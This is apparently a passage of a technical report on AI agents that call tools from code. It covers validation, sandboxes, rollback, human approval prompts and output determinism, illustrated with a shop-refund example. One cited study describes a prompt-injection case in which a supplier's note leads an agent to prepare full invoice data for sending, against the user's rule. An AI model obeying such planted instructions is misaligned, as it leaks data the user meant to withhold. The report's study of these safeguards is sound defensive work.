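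Code has a clearer advantage when the model must make very many independent calls. Claude Sonnet 5 made every required JSON call on tasks with up to 70 calls, but its success rate fell to 75% at 72 calls and to zero at 100 because it left calls out. With code, it was correct every time at both 72 and 100. GPT-5.6 Sol made all 100 JSON calls, so the limit depends on the model. The manager's 40 orders would be within the limit for both models. In this test, code began to use fewer tokens than JSON at about 26 calls.

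The benchmark's functions only returned the arguments they received, without looking anything up or changing anything, which limits what can be concluded from any of these results. In one chain, the model has to find the circumference of a circle with a radius of 7 and then use it as the side of a square. The model's script called the circumference function, ignored the result, calculated 2 × π × 7 itself and passed that number to the next function. The scoring program counted this as correct. On other tasks, models skipped the functions and ranked countries by population from memory.

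A model can do this with circles, but it cannot calculate when order A-1042 arrived. The test therefore measures whether models can write correct arguments in both formats. It gives very little evidence of whether they can pass real results from one tool to the next, which is the main reason to use code.

### Tests in which the tools changed something

Two other studies from 2026 used tools that read and changed records in simulated systems. *E-Bench* (Zheng, Zou and colleagues, 2026) simulates a video game, a music service and a meeting planner, all modelled on Tencent products. Its 323 tasks involve work such as finding a free slot for a group of employees, booking a room and adding the meeting to everyone's calendar. A task changes about 25 database rows on average. A run succeeds only if the final database contains exactly the required changes.

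Eleven models attempted the tasks with ordinary tools, and then again with the option of calling the same tools from Python. The option helped every model, and average success rose from 54.6% to 63.9%. Tool calls per task fell from 60.4 to 15.9, and turns fell from 14.9 to 9.9. A whole script counts as one tool call, though, so the tools themselves may have run just as often. Claude Opus 4.8 rose from 68.8% to 81.1% and took first place from Kimi K3, which gained less than 4 points.

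Code helped most on tasks that required filtering by several conditions, where success rose by 10.6 points. It rose by 7.6 points on tasks that depended on exact limits, such as room capacity. Zheng and colleagues conclude that code takes over calculation more than judgment. The models also used code where it helped most. The largest gains came on the hardest tasks, where they always wrote code, and having the option made almost no difference on tasks where they never did.

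These tasks suit code unusually well because Claude Opus 4.7 wrote them with access to Python and the database, which let it create problems that require computation and more than a single tool call. An agent that mostly handles one request at a time probably wouldn't gain nine points.

Rai's study is smaller but more informative about why code fails. It tested three open models in a simulated company with 42 tools for billing, support, calendars and similar jobs. The models either made ordinary tool calls or could act only through scripts. Each design had the same 119 tasks, and a program checked the state of the company afterwards.

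Rai ran the code version twice. In one run, each tool's description included the format of its result, such as the field names. In the other, it included only the result's type, a dictionary or a list.

| Model | Ordinary calls | Code, result format described | Code, result format missing |
|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3.8 27B | 85.7% | 99.2% | 97.5% |
| Gemma 4 26B | 86.6% | 89.1% | 66.4% |
| Nemotron 3 Nano | 36.1% | 55.5% | 16.0% |

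When the formats were described, code used 70% to 90% fewer tokens than ordinary calls and raised success for all three models, although Gemma's small gain could be due to chance. Without those descriptions, Gemma and Nemotron did far worse with code than with ordinary calls.

The refund script shows the reason. A model that calls `get_order` directly can find the delivery date in the record whatever the field is called, but a model that writes a script has to name the field `delivered_on` before it has seen a record. If the field is really called `delivery_date`, the script fails on the first order. Tool schemas usually describe only the inputs, so a tool that works well for direct calls may lack information that a script needs. In the example that Varda and Pai print, the generated code interface describes the inputs precisely but allows results of any form.

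Adding the result format is therefore probably the easiest improvement a developer can make before letting a model call tools from code. Rai wrote the descriptions by hand and tuned them on practice tasks, so automatically generated ones may help less. The 119 tasks also came from only 21 templates, and all three models ran with their hidden reasoning switched off.

### Coding agents with and without special tools

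In software engineering, the debate has been about whether an agent with a shell also needs special tools. Yang, Jimenez and colleagues (2024) argued in *SWE-agent* that it does. They gave GPT-4 Turbo a small set of commands for searching, viewing and editing files. The viewer showed at most 100 lines at a time, and a search with more than 50 matches returned a prompt to be more specific. The editor checked the code for errors and discarded edits that would have broken it.

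The test was SWE-bench, a collection of real bug reports from open-source Python projects, in which an agent passes if its fix satisfies the project's tests. On 300 of these tasks, the agent with special commands solved 18.0%. With only a shell, the same model solved 11.0% if its prompt included a worked example and 7.3% if it didn't. The frequently cited gain of 10.7 points is measured against the lower figure. A badly designed command could also lower the score. The agent solved 12.0% with a search command that showed matches one at a time, compared with 15.7% when it had no special search command.

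Later models have needed much less help from the harness. SWE-bench now uses mini-SWE-agent, a very simple harness that offers only a shell, to compare models. In Vals AI's *SWE-bench Verified* results from September 2026, Claude Opus 5 solved 97.0% of 500 tasks with it. Those tasks are a different selection from the 300 used in 2024, but that cannot explain a rise from 11% to 97%. Vals AI has stopped running the benchmark on new models because the best ones solve almost all the tasks.

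In the same results, two models were run both with the shell alone and in their provider's own coding harness. Claude Opus 4.8 solved 88.6% of tasks with the shell and 85.8% in Claude Code, and GPT-5.5 solved 82.6% with the shell and 76.4% in Codex. The shell-only runs cost more per task, at $1.92 against $0.67 for Claude Opus 4.8 and $1.36 against $0.65 for GPT-5.5. The harnesses differ in their prompts and settings as well as their tools, so the tools may not be responsible for the difference in either solve rate or cost.

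In *When Does Restricting a Coding Agent to execute_code Help?*, Yang, Yu and Desell (2026) varied each agent's tools and kept the rest of the harness fixed. They ran Claude Code with Claude Sonnet 4.6 and Codex with GPT-5.5, each in three setups: the full set of tools, a shell without the editing tools, and a single tool that runs Python and shell commands. The agents worked on 93 computation tasks and 100 SWE-bench bug fixes, three times each. The table compares the single code tool with the cheaper of the other two setups, which was the shell for computation and the full set for bug fixes.

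| Tasks | Agent | Change in pass rate | Change in cost |
|---|---|---|---|
| Computation | Claude Code | 0.0 points | −24.6% |
| Computation | Codex | +2.5 points | −6.7% (not significant) |
| Bug fixes | Claude Code | −1.7 points | +14.4% (not significant) |
| Bug fixes | Codex | +0.3 points | −19.9% |

None of the differences in pass rate was statistically significant. Costs differed more. With only the code tool, Claude had to write a small script for every file edit, and its output on the bug fixes grew by 40%. But most of the extra cost came from tasks that Claude usually failed with at least one setup. On tasks it usually solved with all three setups, the code tool cost only 4.1% more. Codex's costs on the bug fixes fell because it combined several lookups in one script and printed less of the results. Its longest outputs shrank from about 40,000 characters to 17,000.

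Yang and colleagues found that taking the structured tools away from an agent that already has a shell makes little difference to whether it succeeds. They did not compare schema-validated calls with free-form code, since all three setups could run arbitrary commands. The restriction was also less strict for Codex, which has no setting to disable its editing tool. They could only tell the agent not to use the tool, though it very rarely used it.

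SWE-agent's 2024 result seems to apply mainly to weaker models. GPT-4 Turbo struggled with long search results and made edits that broke the code, so tools that prevented these problems helped. Such tools improve accuracy less for models that rarely make these mistakes, but they may still save money.

### Harm that pass rates don't count

None of these studies reports how much damage the failed runs did. The functions in the Berkeley tests had no effects, so they couldn't damage anything. A bug fix passes if the project's tests pass, even if the agent has also deleted a file that the tests never use. Yang and colleagues turned off permission prompts and the agents' own sandboxes for their runs, and deleted each agent's changes afterwards. That is sensible for an experiment, but it removes the chance for a person to stop a dangerous command.

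E-Bench comes closest to measuring side effects, because an unwanted change to the database makes a run fail. But it counts all failures equally. Suppose each of the manager's 40 orders came to $64.00, so that the shop owes 12 customers a total of $153.60. An agent that refunds nobody would score zero, and so would one that refunds all 40 orders in full, a total of $2,560.

The difference matters more for code than for single calls. A script can issue all 40 wrong refunds before the model gets any result back, while an agent that makes one call per turn could notice the first mistake before making the second. Parallel calls carry much the same risk as a script, except that the harness receives the whole batch before running it. *From Tool Orchestration to Code Execution* (Felendler, Gandhi and colleagues, 2026) found that code saves tokens and time but also exposes the agent to more kinds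 of attack.

A better test would report unwanted changes separately from missing ones and weight the unwanted ones by how hard they are to undo. E-Bench already compares the database before and after each run, so Zheng and colleagues could count the rows that agents changed by mistake, with and without code. They have kept the tasks and environments private to stop developers from training on them, so other researchers would have to build their own.

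## What can be checked before generated code runs

A tool call contains its whole request before anything runs. If the agent calls `issue_refund` with order A-1042, an amount of 1850 cents and the reason `damaged`, a validator or a person can read every value before any money moves. The refund script in the previous section has one line that calls `issue_refund`, but that line could run 40 times or not at all, depending on the delivery dates the script reads while running. A developer can check the script for many kinds of mistake in advance, but usually can't get a list of its refunds without running it.

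### The general limit, and how restricted languages avoid part of it

No program can decide every question about how other programs will behave. Suppose a script runs a long search and then issues a refund. To decide whether it will ever issue the refund, a checker must decide whether the search finishes, and Alan Turing showed in 1936 that no program can do that for all programs. Henry Rice extended the result in 1953 to nearly every property of what a program computes. A checker for a general-purpose language must therefore reject some good programs, accept some bad ones or sometimes give no answer. *The Alignment Problem in Constrained Code Generation* describes a similar choice for software that enforces a complex type system while a model writes code.

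Restricted languages avoid part of this limit by leaving features out. If scripts can loop only over finite lists and functions can't call themselves, every script ends. If the language has no way to open a file, there is no need to check whether a script opens one. Monty, Pydantic's interpreter for a subset of Python, gives scripts no access to files, the network or environment variables by default. Scripts can reach outside systems only through functions that the developer supplies. An early version also lacked classes and much of the standard library, and Pydantic doesn't expect Monty ever to support third-party packages. But even in a very small language, reading a script can't show how many refunds it will issue, because that depends on which parcels were late.

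The table lists some mistakes that the refund script could contain and the first check that would catch each one.

| Mistake | First check that catches it |
|---|---|
| The characters `\n` instead of a real line break | Parsing |
| The reason `"delayed"`, which the tool doesn't accept | Type checking |
| An import of a web library, to query the courier's site directly | List of allowed imports |
| A loop that never ends | The sandbox's time limit |
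| A refund of 0 cents on a free order | The validator, once the script makes the call |
| A total that includes shipping, when the manager meant only the goods | None |

### Parsing, type checking and lists of allowed names

Parsing catches code that isn't valid Python, such as the one-line scripts full of `\n` that three models wrote in the tests by Patel and colleagues. But it misses type errors, such as passing a number to a function that takes a string. In *Type-Constrained Code Generation with Language Models*, Mündler, He and colleagues (2025) had six open models write TypeScript, a typed version of JavaScript. About 94% of the compilation errors were type errors, and the rest were syntax errors.

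To check types in a script that calls tools, the harness needs *stubs*, which give each function's argument and result types without its implementation. For the refund tools they might look like this:

```python
from typing import Literal, TypedDict

class Order(TypedDict):
    total_cents: int
    promised_by: str
    delivered_on: str

async def get_order(order_id: str) -> Order: ...

async def issue_refund(order_id: str, amount_cents: int,
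                       reason: Literal["damaged", "late", "wrong_item"]) -> None: ...
```

With these stubs, a type checker rejects a script before it runs if the script omits the reason, passes the amount as the string `"18.50"` or uses an undeclared `notify_customer`. The harness can generate the argument types from the tool's schema.

Result types are just as useful. The script in the previous section reads each order with `json.loads`, which returns a value of unknown type, so a type checker would accept any field name and any calculation with it. If `get_order` returns an `Order`, the checker can flag `delivery_date` as a field that doesn't exist, the kind of wrong guess that made scripts fail in Rai's tests. It can also flag `/` used in place of `//`, because `/` produces a decimal number in Python and the refund tool takes a whole number.

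Type checking can't show whether the order exists or whether a fifth is the right share, and Python's basic types can't express the schema's minimum of 1 cent. The check also depends on accurate stubs. If the stubs don't allow for an undelivered parcel having no delivery date, the script can pass the check and still crash. But the check is fast. Pydantic measured 4.8 milliseconds to check and run a one-line program in Monty, which is negligible next to the time a model takes to write it.

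A harness can also search the parsed script for imports and function names that aren't permitted. Red Hat checks for forbidden imports before any code reaches its sandbox. One of its two sandboxes runs Pyodide, a version of Python designed for web browsers, outside a browser. Red Hat discovered that the `js` module, which is relatively harmless in a browser, gave scripts in this sandbox access to files, the network and other processes. It disabled the module and added it to the list of forbidden imports.

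A list of forbidden names misses whatever its author didn't think of, so a list of permitted names is safer. A Python script can also build a module's name while it runs, so a search of its text may miss the name. Neither kind of list limits how a script uses a permitted function. A refund script must be allowed to call `issue_refund`, for example, and could still call it with the wrong amount.

### Enforcing types while the model writes

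Constrained decoding can also enforce a language's typing rules, so that any program the model finishes has no type errors. In one example from Mündler and colleagues, `num` is a number and the model has written `parseInt(num`. A grammar would allow a comma next, but the typing rules don't, because the function's first argument must be a string. The software searches for operations that turn a number into a string, finds `.toString()` and lets the model continue with that.

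Context-free grammars, which providers use to enforce schemas, can't in general express such rules. Testing every token in the vocabulary against the rules was too slow, and every run hit the five-minute time limit. Mündler and colleagues instead draw one token, test it, and draw another only if the test fails. With their smallest model, the first draw passed 99.4% of the time.

On two sets of short programming problems, HumanEval and MBPP, this method reduced the number of programs that failed to compile by 74.8% and 56.0%. Perfect syntax enforcement would have reduced that number by only 9.0% and 4.8%. Correctness improved much less. For example, Qwen2.5 32B solved 81.8% of HumanEval with the typing rules and 79.6% without them. Generation took 39% longer on HumanEval and 52% longer on MBPP.

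The experiment's setup favoured the constraint, however. The software supports only part of TypeScript, so Mündler and colleagues kept every program that compiled without the constraint and applied it only to new attempts at those that didn't. In June 2026, *The Alignment Problem in Constrained Code Generation* tested the same six models with the constraint on from the start. All six did better without it. Qwen2.5 32B solved 82.3% of HumanEval problems unconstrained and 72.3% constrained.

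The constraint did harm by blocking good programs. Gemma 2 2B wrote 4,231 unconstrained programs that compiled, and the software would have rejected 982 of them. In one program, the model called a helper function, `isPalindrome`, before defining it, which the software doesn't support. Under the constraint, the model had already written `is` when the software blocked the rest of the name, so it continued with `isNaN`, a built-in function that does something else. The resulting program had correct types but gave wrong answers.

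Applying the typing rules only after a program fails to compile is a sensible design. When the models had to repair such programs, the rules raised the share of working repairs by an average of 37% in relative terms. But newer models probably have little to gain, because 98.1% of the HumanEval programs that Qwen2.5 32B, a 2024 model, wrote without constraints already compiled in the 2026 test. For most agents, it is simpler to run a type checker on the finished script and return the errors to the model.

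### What a sandbox limits

A sandbox limits the code's access, time and memory, but doesn't check the code itself. According to Anthropic's *Code execution tool*, Claude's code runs in a Linux container with 5 GiB of memory, 5 GiB of disk space and one processor. The code can't reach the internet, even to install a package, and can access only its own workspace directory. With programmatic tool calling, each block of Python must also finish within 90 seconds. Anthropic warns that if a developer also gives Claude a separate shell, the model may act as if the two environments shared files.

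Red Hat's other sandbox runs the code as an unprivileged user in a container with no network and a read-only file system. Passwords and access keys stay outside the container, and the host adds them when it makes the tool call. Cloudflare uses the same arrangement, and Varda and Pai point out that the model therefore can't write code that leaks a key.

Pydantic's *Monty* gives startup times of 0.8 milliseconds for a new Monty sandbox, 195 for a local Docker container and 1,500 for a hosted sandboxing service. The comparison favours Pydantic's own product, because Monty's figure is for a sandbox from a pool the application has already created, while the others start from scratch. Monty also enforces memory limits inside the interpreter, so a script that tries to create a string of a trillion characters gets an error before the computer tries to allocate the memory.

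Sandboxes can fail. Reuters reported in December 2026 that Anthropic and OpenAI had disclosed cases of agents escaping test environments. But even a sandbox that works perfectly would let the script issue 40 wrong refunds, because the developer gave the script a tool for issuing refunds.

### Twenty-two refunds paid and an error

With programmatic tool calling, the harness still checks each call against its schema, but only when the script reaches that call. A harness that receives 40 direct calls in one response can validate them all before executing any. If a script makes those calls one after another, the harness can't validate the 23rd until the first 22 have run.

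Suppose all 40 orders on the manager's list arrived late. The 23rd was a free replacement for a lost parcel, so its total is zero and the script tries to refund 0 cents. The validator rejects the call, and the script stops with an error. The shop has already refunded 22 customers, but the script has not reached the last 17 orders.

The model reads the error, adds a line that skips free orders and reruns the script from the beginning. The first 22 customers receive a second refund. Every call in this run is valid, and the payment system accepts the repeats because 80% of each order's price is still refundable. The earlier script prints its list of refunded orders only at the end, so the error message alone doesn't show which customers have been refunded. Variables normally persist between blocks of code in Anthropic's container, so the model could look up the list, but it isn't required to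 do so before rerunning the script.

*Evidence-Guided Recovery for AI Agents with Ambiguous Tool Outcomes and Partial Execution* (Zhu, Chen and colleagues, 2026) describes a harder case, in which a call times out and the agent can't tell whether the action failed, succeeded or is still in progress. This can easily happen with programmatic tool calling, where a call raises a timeout error if its result takes more than about four minutes to reach Claude's script. Anthropic notes that Claude typically retries. If the call was issuing a refund and the payment system was only slow, the retry may refund the customer twice.

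### Preventing and repairing half-finished work

A *dry run* executes the script with `issue_refund` replaced by a function that only records its arguments. The harness can then validate all 40 calls and find the zero before anyone receives money. But someone has to build the recording function, and if the script needs the result of one write for its next step, the dry run can continue only with an invented result. Orders may also change between the dry run and the real one. To avoid recalculating the refunds, the harness can pay from the recorded list instead of running the script again. OpenAI's advice to keep writes as direct calls has a similar effect, because the script then only prepares the refunds.

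A *transaction* makes a group of changes succeed or fail together. If the refunds were only entries in the shop's own database, the database could discard the first 22 when the 23rd failed, but it can't recall money that has already gone to customers' banks. *Cordon* (2026), a transaction system for agents, therefore rolls back local changes but delays, audits or compensates for outside effects. *Atomix* (2026) lets developers group the effects that must settle together. Holding every refund until the script finishes would have prevented the half-paid batch, but it would also slow payments and require extra software around each tool. Some outside services can't take part in such a group.

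An *idempotency key* is an identifier attached to a request so that the receiving service can recognise a repeat. If the refund for order A-1042 always carries the key `late-A-1042`, the service can return the earlier result instead of paying again, and the corrected script can safely start from the top. The key has to be based on the order and the purpose of the refund, because if the script generates random keys, a second run produces 22 new ones and the customers are refunded twice. The service also has to support keys. *RetryBench* (2026) notes that the payment company Stripe's guarantee depends on how long it keeps keys and whether the repeated request has the same parameters. If the corrected script also changes the amounts, the shop can't rely on the old keys.

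Without keys, the agent can check which refunds went through and send only the missing ones. *Where Does Exactly-Once Live?* (2026) recommends this for a batch that times out after completing its first half. This approach fails if a payment is still in progress. In another of the benchmark's test cases, an action takes effect 90 seconds after the timeout, so an agent that checks too early finds nothing and may repeat the action.

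Developers can also give each tool a way to undo its action. Cloudflare's *How Code Mode works* describes an optional `revert` function for each method, and a rollback calls these functions in reverse order. Methods without one stay applied, and a `revert` call can itself fail. The software marks the whole run as rolled back if it reversed even one call, so the label doesn't guarantee that everything was undone. To reverse a refund, the shop would have to charge the customer again, which it may have no right to do.

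Some actions cannot be undone. *A Five-Plane Reference Architecture for Runtime Governance of Production AI Agents* (2026) gives the example of a sent email, and adds that undoing actions is harder when several agents work on the same systems. *Always-On Agents* (2026), a survey of long-running agents, found a rollback mechanism in only 27 of 435 works.

Whichever remedy a team chooses, it should probably put the recovery rules in the harness. In simulated tests by Zhu and colleagues, a planning algorithm and three simpler sets of rules each brought 28 of 37 interrupted tasks to a confirmed, safe finish. In a separate test, two locally run language models did so in only 9 of 58 cases when given the evidence alone, and in 30 when the software also recommended the next action. The simpler rules did as well as the planner in the first test, so they may be enough.

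### What a person can approve

A reviewer can check the refund for the broken mug by comparing three values with the customer's message. To check a 40-line script, they have to read Python, know what `total_cents` includes and work out what each line will do with records they haven't seen. One advantage of code is that the formula appears only once, so a reviewer who notices that the total includes shipping can prevent 40 mistakes.

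Approval prompts for code often show very little. *Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) points out that a person who approves the command `python3 setup.py` approves whatever that file contains. Weak user review was a factor in 105 of the 290 reports the paper covers. In 80 of them, users had let the agent act without asking, and in 31, the prompt told them too little. Some users turned off the prompts to avoid answering hundreds in a session.

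Hossain, Shayoni and colleagues (2026), in *When a Permitted Action Completes a Forbidden Workflow*, tested how much the approval prompt matters. Eighty volunteers, 20 for each version of the prompt, each approved or denied 12 proposed actions, half of them unsafe. In one scenario, a user asks an agent to send an auditor only summary totals, but instructions hidden in a supplier's note lead the agent to copy the full invoice rows into `report.csv`. The agent then asks to send that file to the auditor. The recipient and the tool are both permitted, but sending this file breaks the user's rule.

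| What the prompt showed | Unsafe actions approved | Legitimate actions approved | Median time |
|---|---|---|---|
| A short description | 55.0% | 91.7% | 16.3 s |
| The exact arguments as well | 43.3% | 90.0% | 23.4 s |
| Also the user's instructions and a full log | 32.5% | 87.5% | 38.6 s |
| The same facts, organised around the consequence | 24.2% | 85.8% | 33.2 s |

More information helped, but even with the best prompt, people approved about a quarter of the unsafe actions. The advantage of the consequence summary over the log could be due to chance. The volunteers also saw far more unsafe requests than most users would, which may have made them more careful. None of them reviewed code. A script is probably harder to review than a log of what has happened, because the reviewer has to predict what the script will do.

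Cloudflare lets developers require approval for individual methods, so people don't have to judge the whole script. One of its examples does this for a method that saves documents. When the script reaches such a method, the software stops and can show a person the pending call with its arguments. The person can take as long as they need. If they approve, the software reruns the script from the beginning but returns the recorded results of earlier calls instead of repeating them. If they reject the call, the script ends, but the earlier actions stand, so rejecting the 23rd refund would leave 22 paid.

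In Anthropic's version, the limit of about four minutes also applies to calls waiting for approval. If the manager doesn't respond in time, the call times out and Claude may send it again. The manager could then find two requests for the same refund and approve both. Anthropic advises against programmatic tool calling for tools that need immediate user feedback between calls.

Separate approvals also become tedious. At the study's median of 23.4 seconds for a prompt with exact arguments, 40 refunds would take almost 16 minutes, and few people would read the last prompt as carefully as the first. *Let the Agent Do It?* (2026), a study of software practitioners, warns that repeated approval may reflect fatigue rather than preference. It recommends showing more clearly what an action will do and whether it can be undone.

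For the late parcels, a dry run can provide such a summary. The manager would see a table of 40 orders with the price, delay and proposed refund for each, the total at the bottom, and a note that the shop can't easily take the money back. The 0-cent refund would stand out, and an unexpectedly high total might too. If the harness then executes only the calls in that table, the manager has approved specific payments, and any change to the script needs a new approval.

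## What repeats from run to run

If the manager runs the refund agent twice on the same list of orders, the same customers should get the same money both times. People call an agent deterministic when they expect this of it, but the word covers four different properties, and a schema ensures only one of them.

| What repeats | In the refund example | What a schema contributes |
|---|---|---|
| The validator's verdict | The amount `"18.50"` fails every time | Secures it |
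| The tool's effect | The same call, on the same records, pays out the same money | Nothing |
| The model's call | The same message about the mug leads to the same call | Fewer calls to choose from |
| The task's outcome | The customer gets exactly $18.50 on every attempt | No guarantee |

The validator's verdict on a call changes only if someone edits the schema or the validator.

A tool's effect depends on code that the schema doesn't describe. A refund tool might convert currencies at the current rate and pay out different amounts for identical calls. For a fair comparison, runs also have to start from the same state, because the first refund may leave no balance for a second.

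A schema narrows the calls a model can make, for example by limiting `reason` to three values. But the model may still write an amount of 1850 in one run and 6400 in the next, because the schema accepts both.

Yagubyan (2026), in *How Consistent Are LLM Agents?*, measured how much tool calls vary when an agent repeats the same task. Six models from 2024 and 2025 each attempted 19 tasks ten times at a temperature of 1.0, a common default. The simulated tools took typed arguments and always returned the same result for the same input. On a scale where 1 means identical, the sequences of tools scored 0.87 on average and the arguments 0.69. The arguments varied most on vague requests such as "Help me prepare for my meetings tomorrow", where they scored 0.52. The models did not differ significantly in how consistent their arguments were, so making requests clearer would probably help more than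 switching models.

Much of the variation in arguments was harmless, such as a differently worded search query, and Yagubyan found no significant link between consistent arguments and correct results. That finding doesn't apply to refunds, where a different amount always matters. Variation in the choice of tools was more strongly linked to incorrect results. When a model used nearly the same sequence of tools every time, 90.2% of its runs were correct, compared with 61.2% when the sequences varied more.

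The outcome of a task can vary even when an agent's overall score doesn't. In *ComponentBench* (2026), a test of agents that operate graphical interfaces, one setup with GPT-5 mini passed 52.5% of 278 tasks in each of two runs. But 17.3% of the tasks had a different result in the second run, with about 24 going from pass to fail and the same number from fail to pass.

### Why temperature zero is not enough

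A model often produces different text from the same prompt even at temperature zero, a setting that should prevent this because the software always takes the most probable token instead of drawing one at random. The best-known explanation is Horace He's *Defeating Nondeterminism in LLM Inference*, published in September 2025 in *Connectionism*, the research series of the AI company Thinking Machines Lab. The lab sent one prompt 1,000 times to a model with 235 billion parameters at temperature zero and got 80 different completions, as Khatchadourian and Franco (2025) recount in *LLM Output Drift*.

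The cause lies in how computers round numbers. Suppose a computer keeps only three significant digits. The order in which it adds three numbers can then change the total:

```
(100 + 0.4) + 0.4  →  100 + 0.4  →  100
100 + (0.4 + 0.4)  →  100 + 0.8  →  101
```

Real hardware keeps more digits, but a model's probabilities come from very long sums, and a graphics processor splits each sum into pieces that it adds in parallel. For speed, the software chooses the split according to the size of the *batch*, the group of requests that the server is processing together. The batch contains whatever requests are active, so the shop's prompt may give slightly different probabilities on a busy afternoon than at night. Willison (2025) quotes the post's conclusion that varying load is the main reason nearly all model services are nondeterministic, including those that run on other kinds of processor.

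The rounding differences are tiny and usually don't change the output. But if two tokens are almost tied, a rounding difference can decide which one scores higher, and the model then continues from different text. For a mug that arrived cracked and in the wrong colour, the tie might be between `damaged` and `wrong_item`. In *LLM-42*, Gond, Kamath and colleagues (2026) ran 350 requests through Llama 3.1 8B one at a time and then again in changing batches. The two outputs for each request typically matched for hundreds of tokens, but after the first difference, most pairs diverged almost completely.

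Horace He's solution was a set of *batch-invariant kernels*, low-level routines that add numbers in the same order whatever the batch size. LMSYS's *Towards Deterministic Inference in SGLang and Reproducible RL Training* (2025) describes how the serving software SGLang adopted them. In tests with varying batches, Qwen3 8B produced up to 18 different outputs in 50 trials in normal mode and only one in deterministic mode. SGLang can also repeat random choices if the developer supplies a seed, so repeatable output doesn't require a temperature of zero.

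Those tests also cast doubt on advice from Khatchadourian and Franco, who recommend small models for regulated financial work. At temperature zero, their two models with 7 and 8 billion parameters produced identical output every time, while GPT-OSS 120B did so only 12.5% of the time. But Qwen3 8B is just as small and its output still varied, so size alone doesn't make a model repeatable. In Khatchadourian and Franco's comparison of tasks at a temperature of 0.2, database queries remained stable, but answers drawn from long financial filings were identical only 25% to 75% of the time. A narrow output format may well help a model produce the same output each time, although the tasks also differed in other ways.

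LMSYS reports that deterministic inference causes a slowdown of 61.5% with the original kernels and 34.35% on average with SGLang's version. One deterministic request can also slow the others in its batch. In a test by Gond and colleagues, a server handling 11 ordinary requests generated 931 tokens a second. When one of the 11 needed deterministic output, the whole batch had to use the slower kernels, and the rate fell to 415 tokens a second.

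Newer methods try to keep the fast kernels. Gond and colleagues generate text at full speed, recompute it in short stretches under fixed conditions, and go back to the last matching token if the results disagree. More than half of the requests never need this correction. In *CoRun*, Zhao, Yang and colleagues (2026) process each prompt alone and then pad every batch to the same size during generation, so the sums always split the same way. One generation step took 19.4 milliseconds normally, 88.4 with batch-invariant kernels and 32.6 with padding. Their guarantee holds only for the same model weights, settings, hardware and software, and developers using hosted models usually control few of these.

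Even perfectly deterministic inference guarantees the same output only when the prompt is identical. The next customer with a broken mug will have a different order number and describe the damage in different words, and nothing guarantees that the model will treat the two messages alike. If it misreads the first message, it will also misread it on every replay and refund $64.00 each time. Exact replay helps explain why a run failed, but it does much less for reliability. LMSYS recommends its deterministic mode mainly for debugging and reproducibility.

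### Measuring repeated success

Reliability depends on how often an agent succeeds when it faces the same task again. Yao, Shinn and colleagues (2024), in *τ-bench*, proposed a measure for this called *pass^k* ("pass hat k"), the chance that all `k` attempts at a task succeed, averaged over tasks. If an agent attempts a task `n` times and succeeds `c` times, the estimate for that task is

```
pass^k = C(c, k) / C(n, k)
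```

where `C(c, k)` is the number of ways to pick `k` attempts from the `c` successful ones. For example, an agent that succeeds in 6 of 8 attempts has a pass^2 of 15/28, or about 54%, on that task. The older measure *pass@k* is the chance that at least one of `k` attempts succeeds. It suits work such as programming, where tests can pick out the good attempt, but a shop can't issue eight refunds and keep the best one.

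Two agents with the same average can have very different values of pass^k:

| | Every task succeeds 90% of the time | 90% of tasks always succeed, 10% never do |
|---|---|---|
| Average success | 90% | 90% |
| pass^8 | 0.9⁸ ≈ 43% | 90% |
| pass@8 | Almost 100% | 90% |

The 43% comes from the same multiplication as the earlier 50-call example, with repeated attempts instead of calls. An agent that fails at random can fail any customer, and testing each task once won't show which tasks might fail later. Retrying helps this agent if something detects the failure. Retrying doesn't help an agent that always fails the same tenth of its tasks, but the shop can find those tasks in testing and give them to its staff.

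In τ-bench, a language model plays a customer of an online shop or an airline, and the agent has to follow the company's policy while using typed tools. A run succeeds if the final database is correct and the agent has told the customer all the required information. The tools behave identically every time and the agent ran at temperature zero, but the simulated customer's wording varied. In 2024, GPT-4o succeeded on 61.2% of attempts at the shop tasks, but its pass^8, the chance of succeeding in all eight attempts at the same task, was below 25%.

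Newer models do much better. *GRADUS* (2026) reports results on τ²-bench, a successor in which the simulated customer can also take actions. Claude Opus 4.5 averaged 90%, with a pass^3 of 82%, and GPT-5.2 averaged 86%, with a pass^3 of 76%. If Claude had a 90% chance of passing each task, its pass^3 would be only 73%, so its failures must be concentrated in certain tasks.

On harder benchmarks, there is still a large gap between the share of tasks agents solve at least once and the share they solve every time. In E-Bench, which tests agents on simulated Tencent products, Zheng and colleagues found that Kimi K3 with ordinary tool calls solved 87.6% of tasks at least once in three attempts, but only 58.8% all three times. In *τ-Emotion-Bench* (2026), where simulated customers express emotions, even the strongest agents solved only about a third of tasks in all three trials.

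*One Success Isn't Reliability* (Li, Ko and colleagues, 2026) gives the most detailed current results. Its benchmark has 507 tasks in retail, hotel bookings, car insurance and two kinds of staff support. Each model attempted every task 20 times with typed tools, and a program checked the final database for wrong, missing and extra changes. The table groups the tasks by whether the model passed all, some or none of its 20 attempts.

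| Model | Average success | Passed all 20 | Passed some | Passed none |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 5 | 66.5% | 47.5% | 31.6% | 20.9% |
| GPT-5.4 | 65.4% | 25.2% | 65.9% | 8.9% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 61.9% | 16.2% | 70.6% | 13.2% |
| GPT-6 Astra | 58.3% | 45.6% | 25.4% | 29.0% |
| Kimi K3 | 57.4% | 13.4% | 80.5% | 6.1% |
| Qwen3.8 27B | 51.7% | 7.5% | 81.9% | 10.7% |

Claude Opus 5 and GPT-5.4 have almost the same average, but Claude is nearly twice as likely to pass a task all 20 times. GPT-6 Astra averages 7 points less than GPT-5.4 but is far more repeatable, with three quarters of its tasks having the same result on every attempt, whether pass or fail. Kimi K3, by contrast, solved 94% of the tasks at least once but only 13% every time.

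The figures for all 20 attempts are somewhat harsh because Li and colleagues count technical errors as failures. A random error in 1% of attempts would by itself cut a perfect agent's score to 82% (0.99²⁰). The simulated customer's wording also varied, so the figures measure how well an agent handles a range of conversations rather than the same one repeated. The published pass^20 values are higher for most models (30.6% for GPT-5.4) because their formula gives partial credit for tasks that succeeded in, for example, 19 of the 20 attempts.

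The agents often failed without any obvious sign. Li and colleagues analyzed 79,853 failed runs by 12 models and found that 80.9% ended normally after the agent had used at least one tool that changes records. In 43.3% of the failures, the database contained changes nobody had asked for. All these agents used typed tools, so schemas don't make outcomes repeat, but we can't tell from these benchmarks whether agents that write code would do better.

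### Scripts that someone has saved and reviewed

Code is more repeatable when the script is saved and reused, because a program follows the same steps every time it runs on the same data. With CodeAct or programmatic tool calling, however, the model normally writes a new script for each request. For example, its formula for late-parcel refunds could include the shipping charge this week and leave it out next week.

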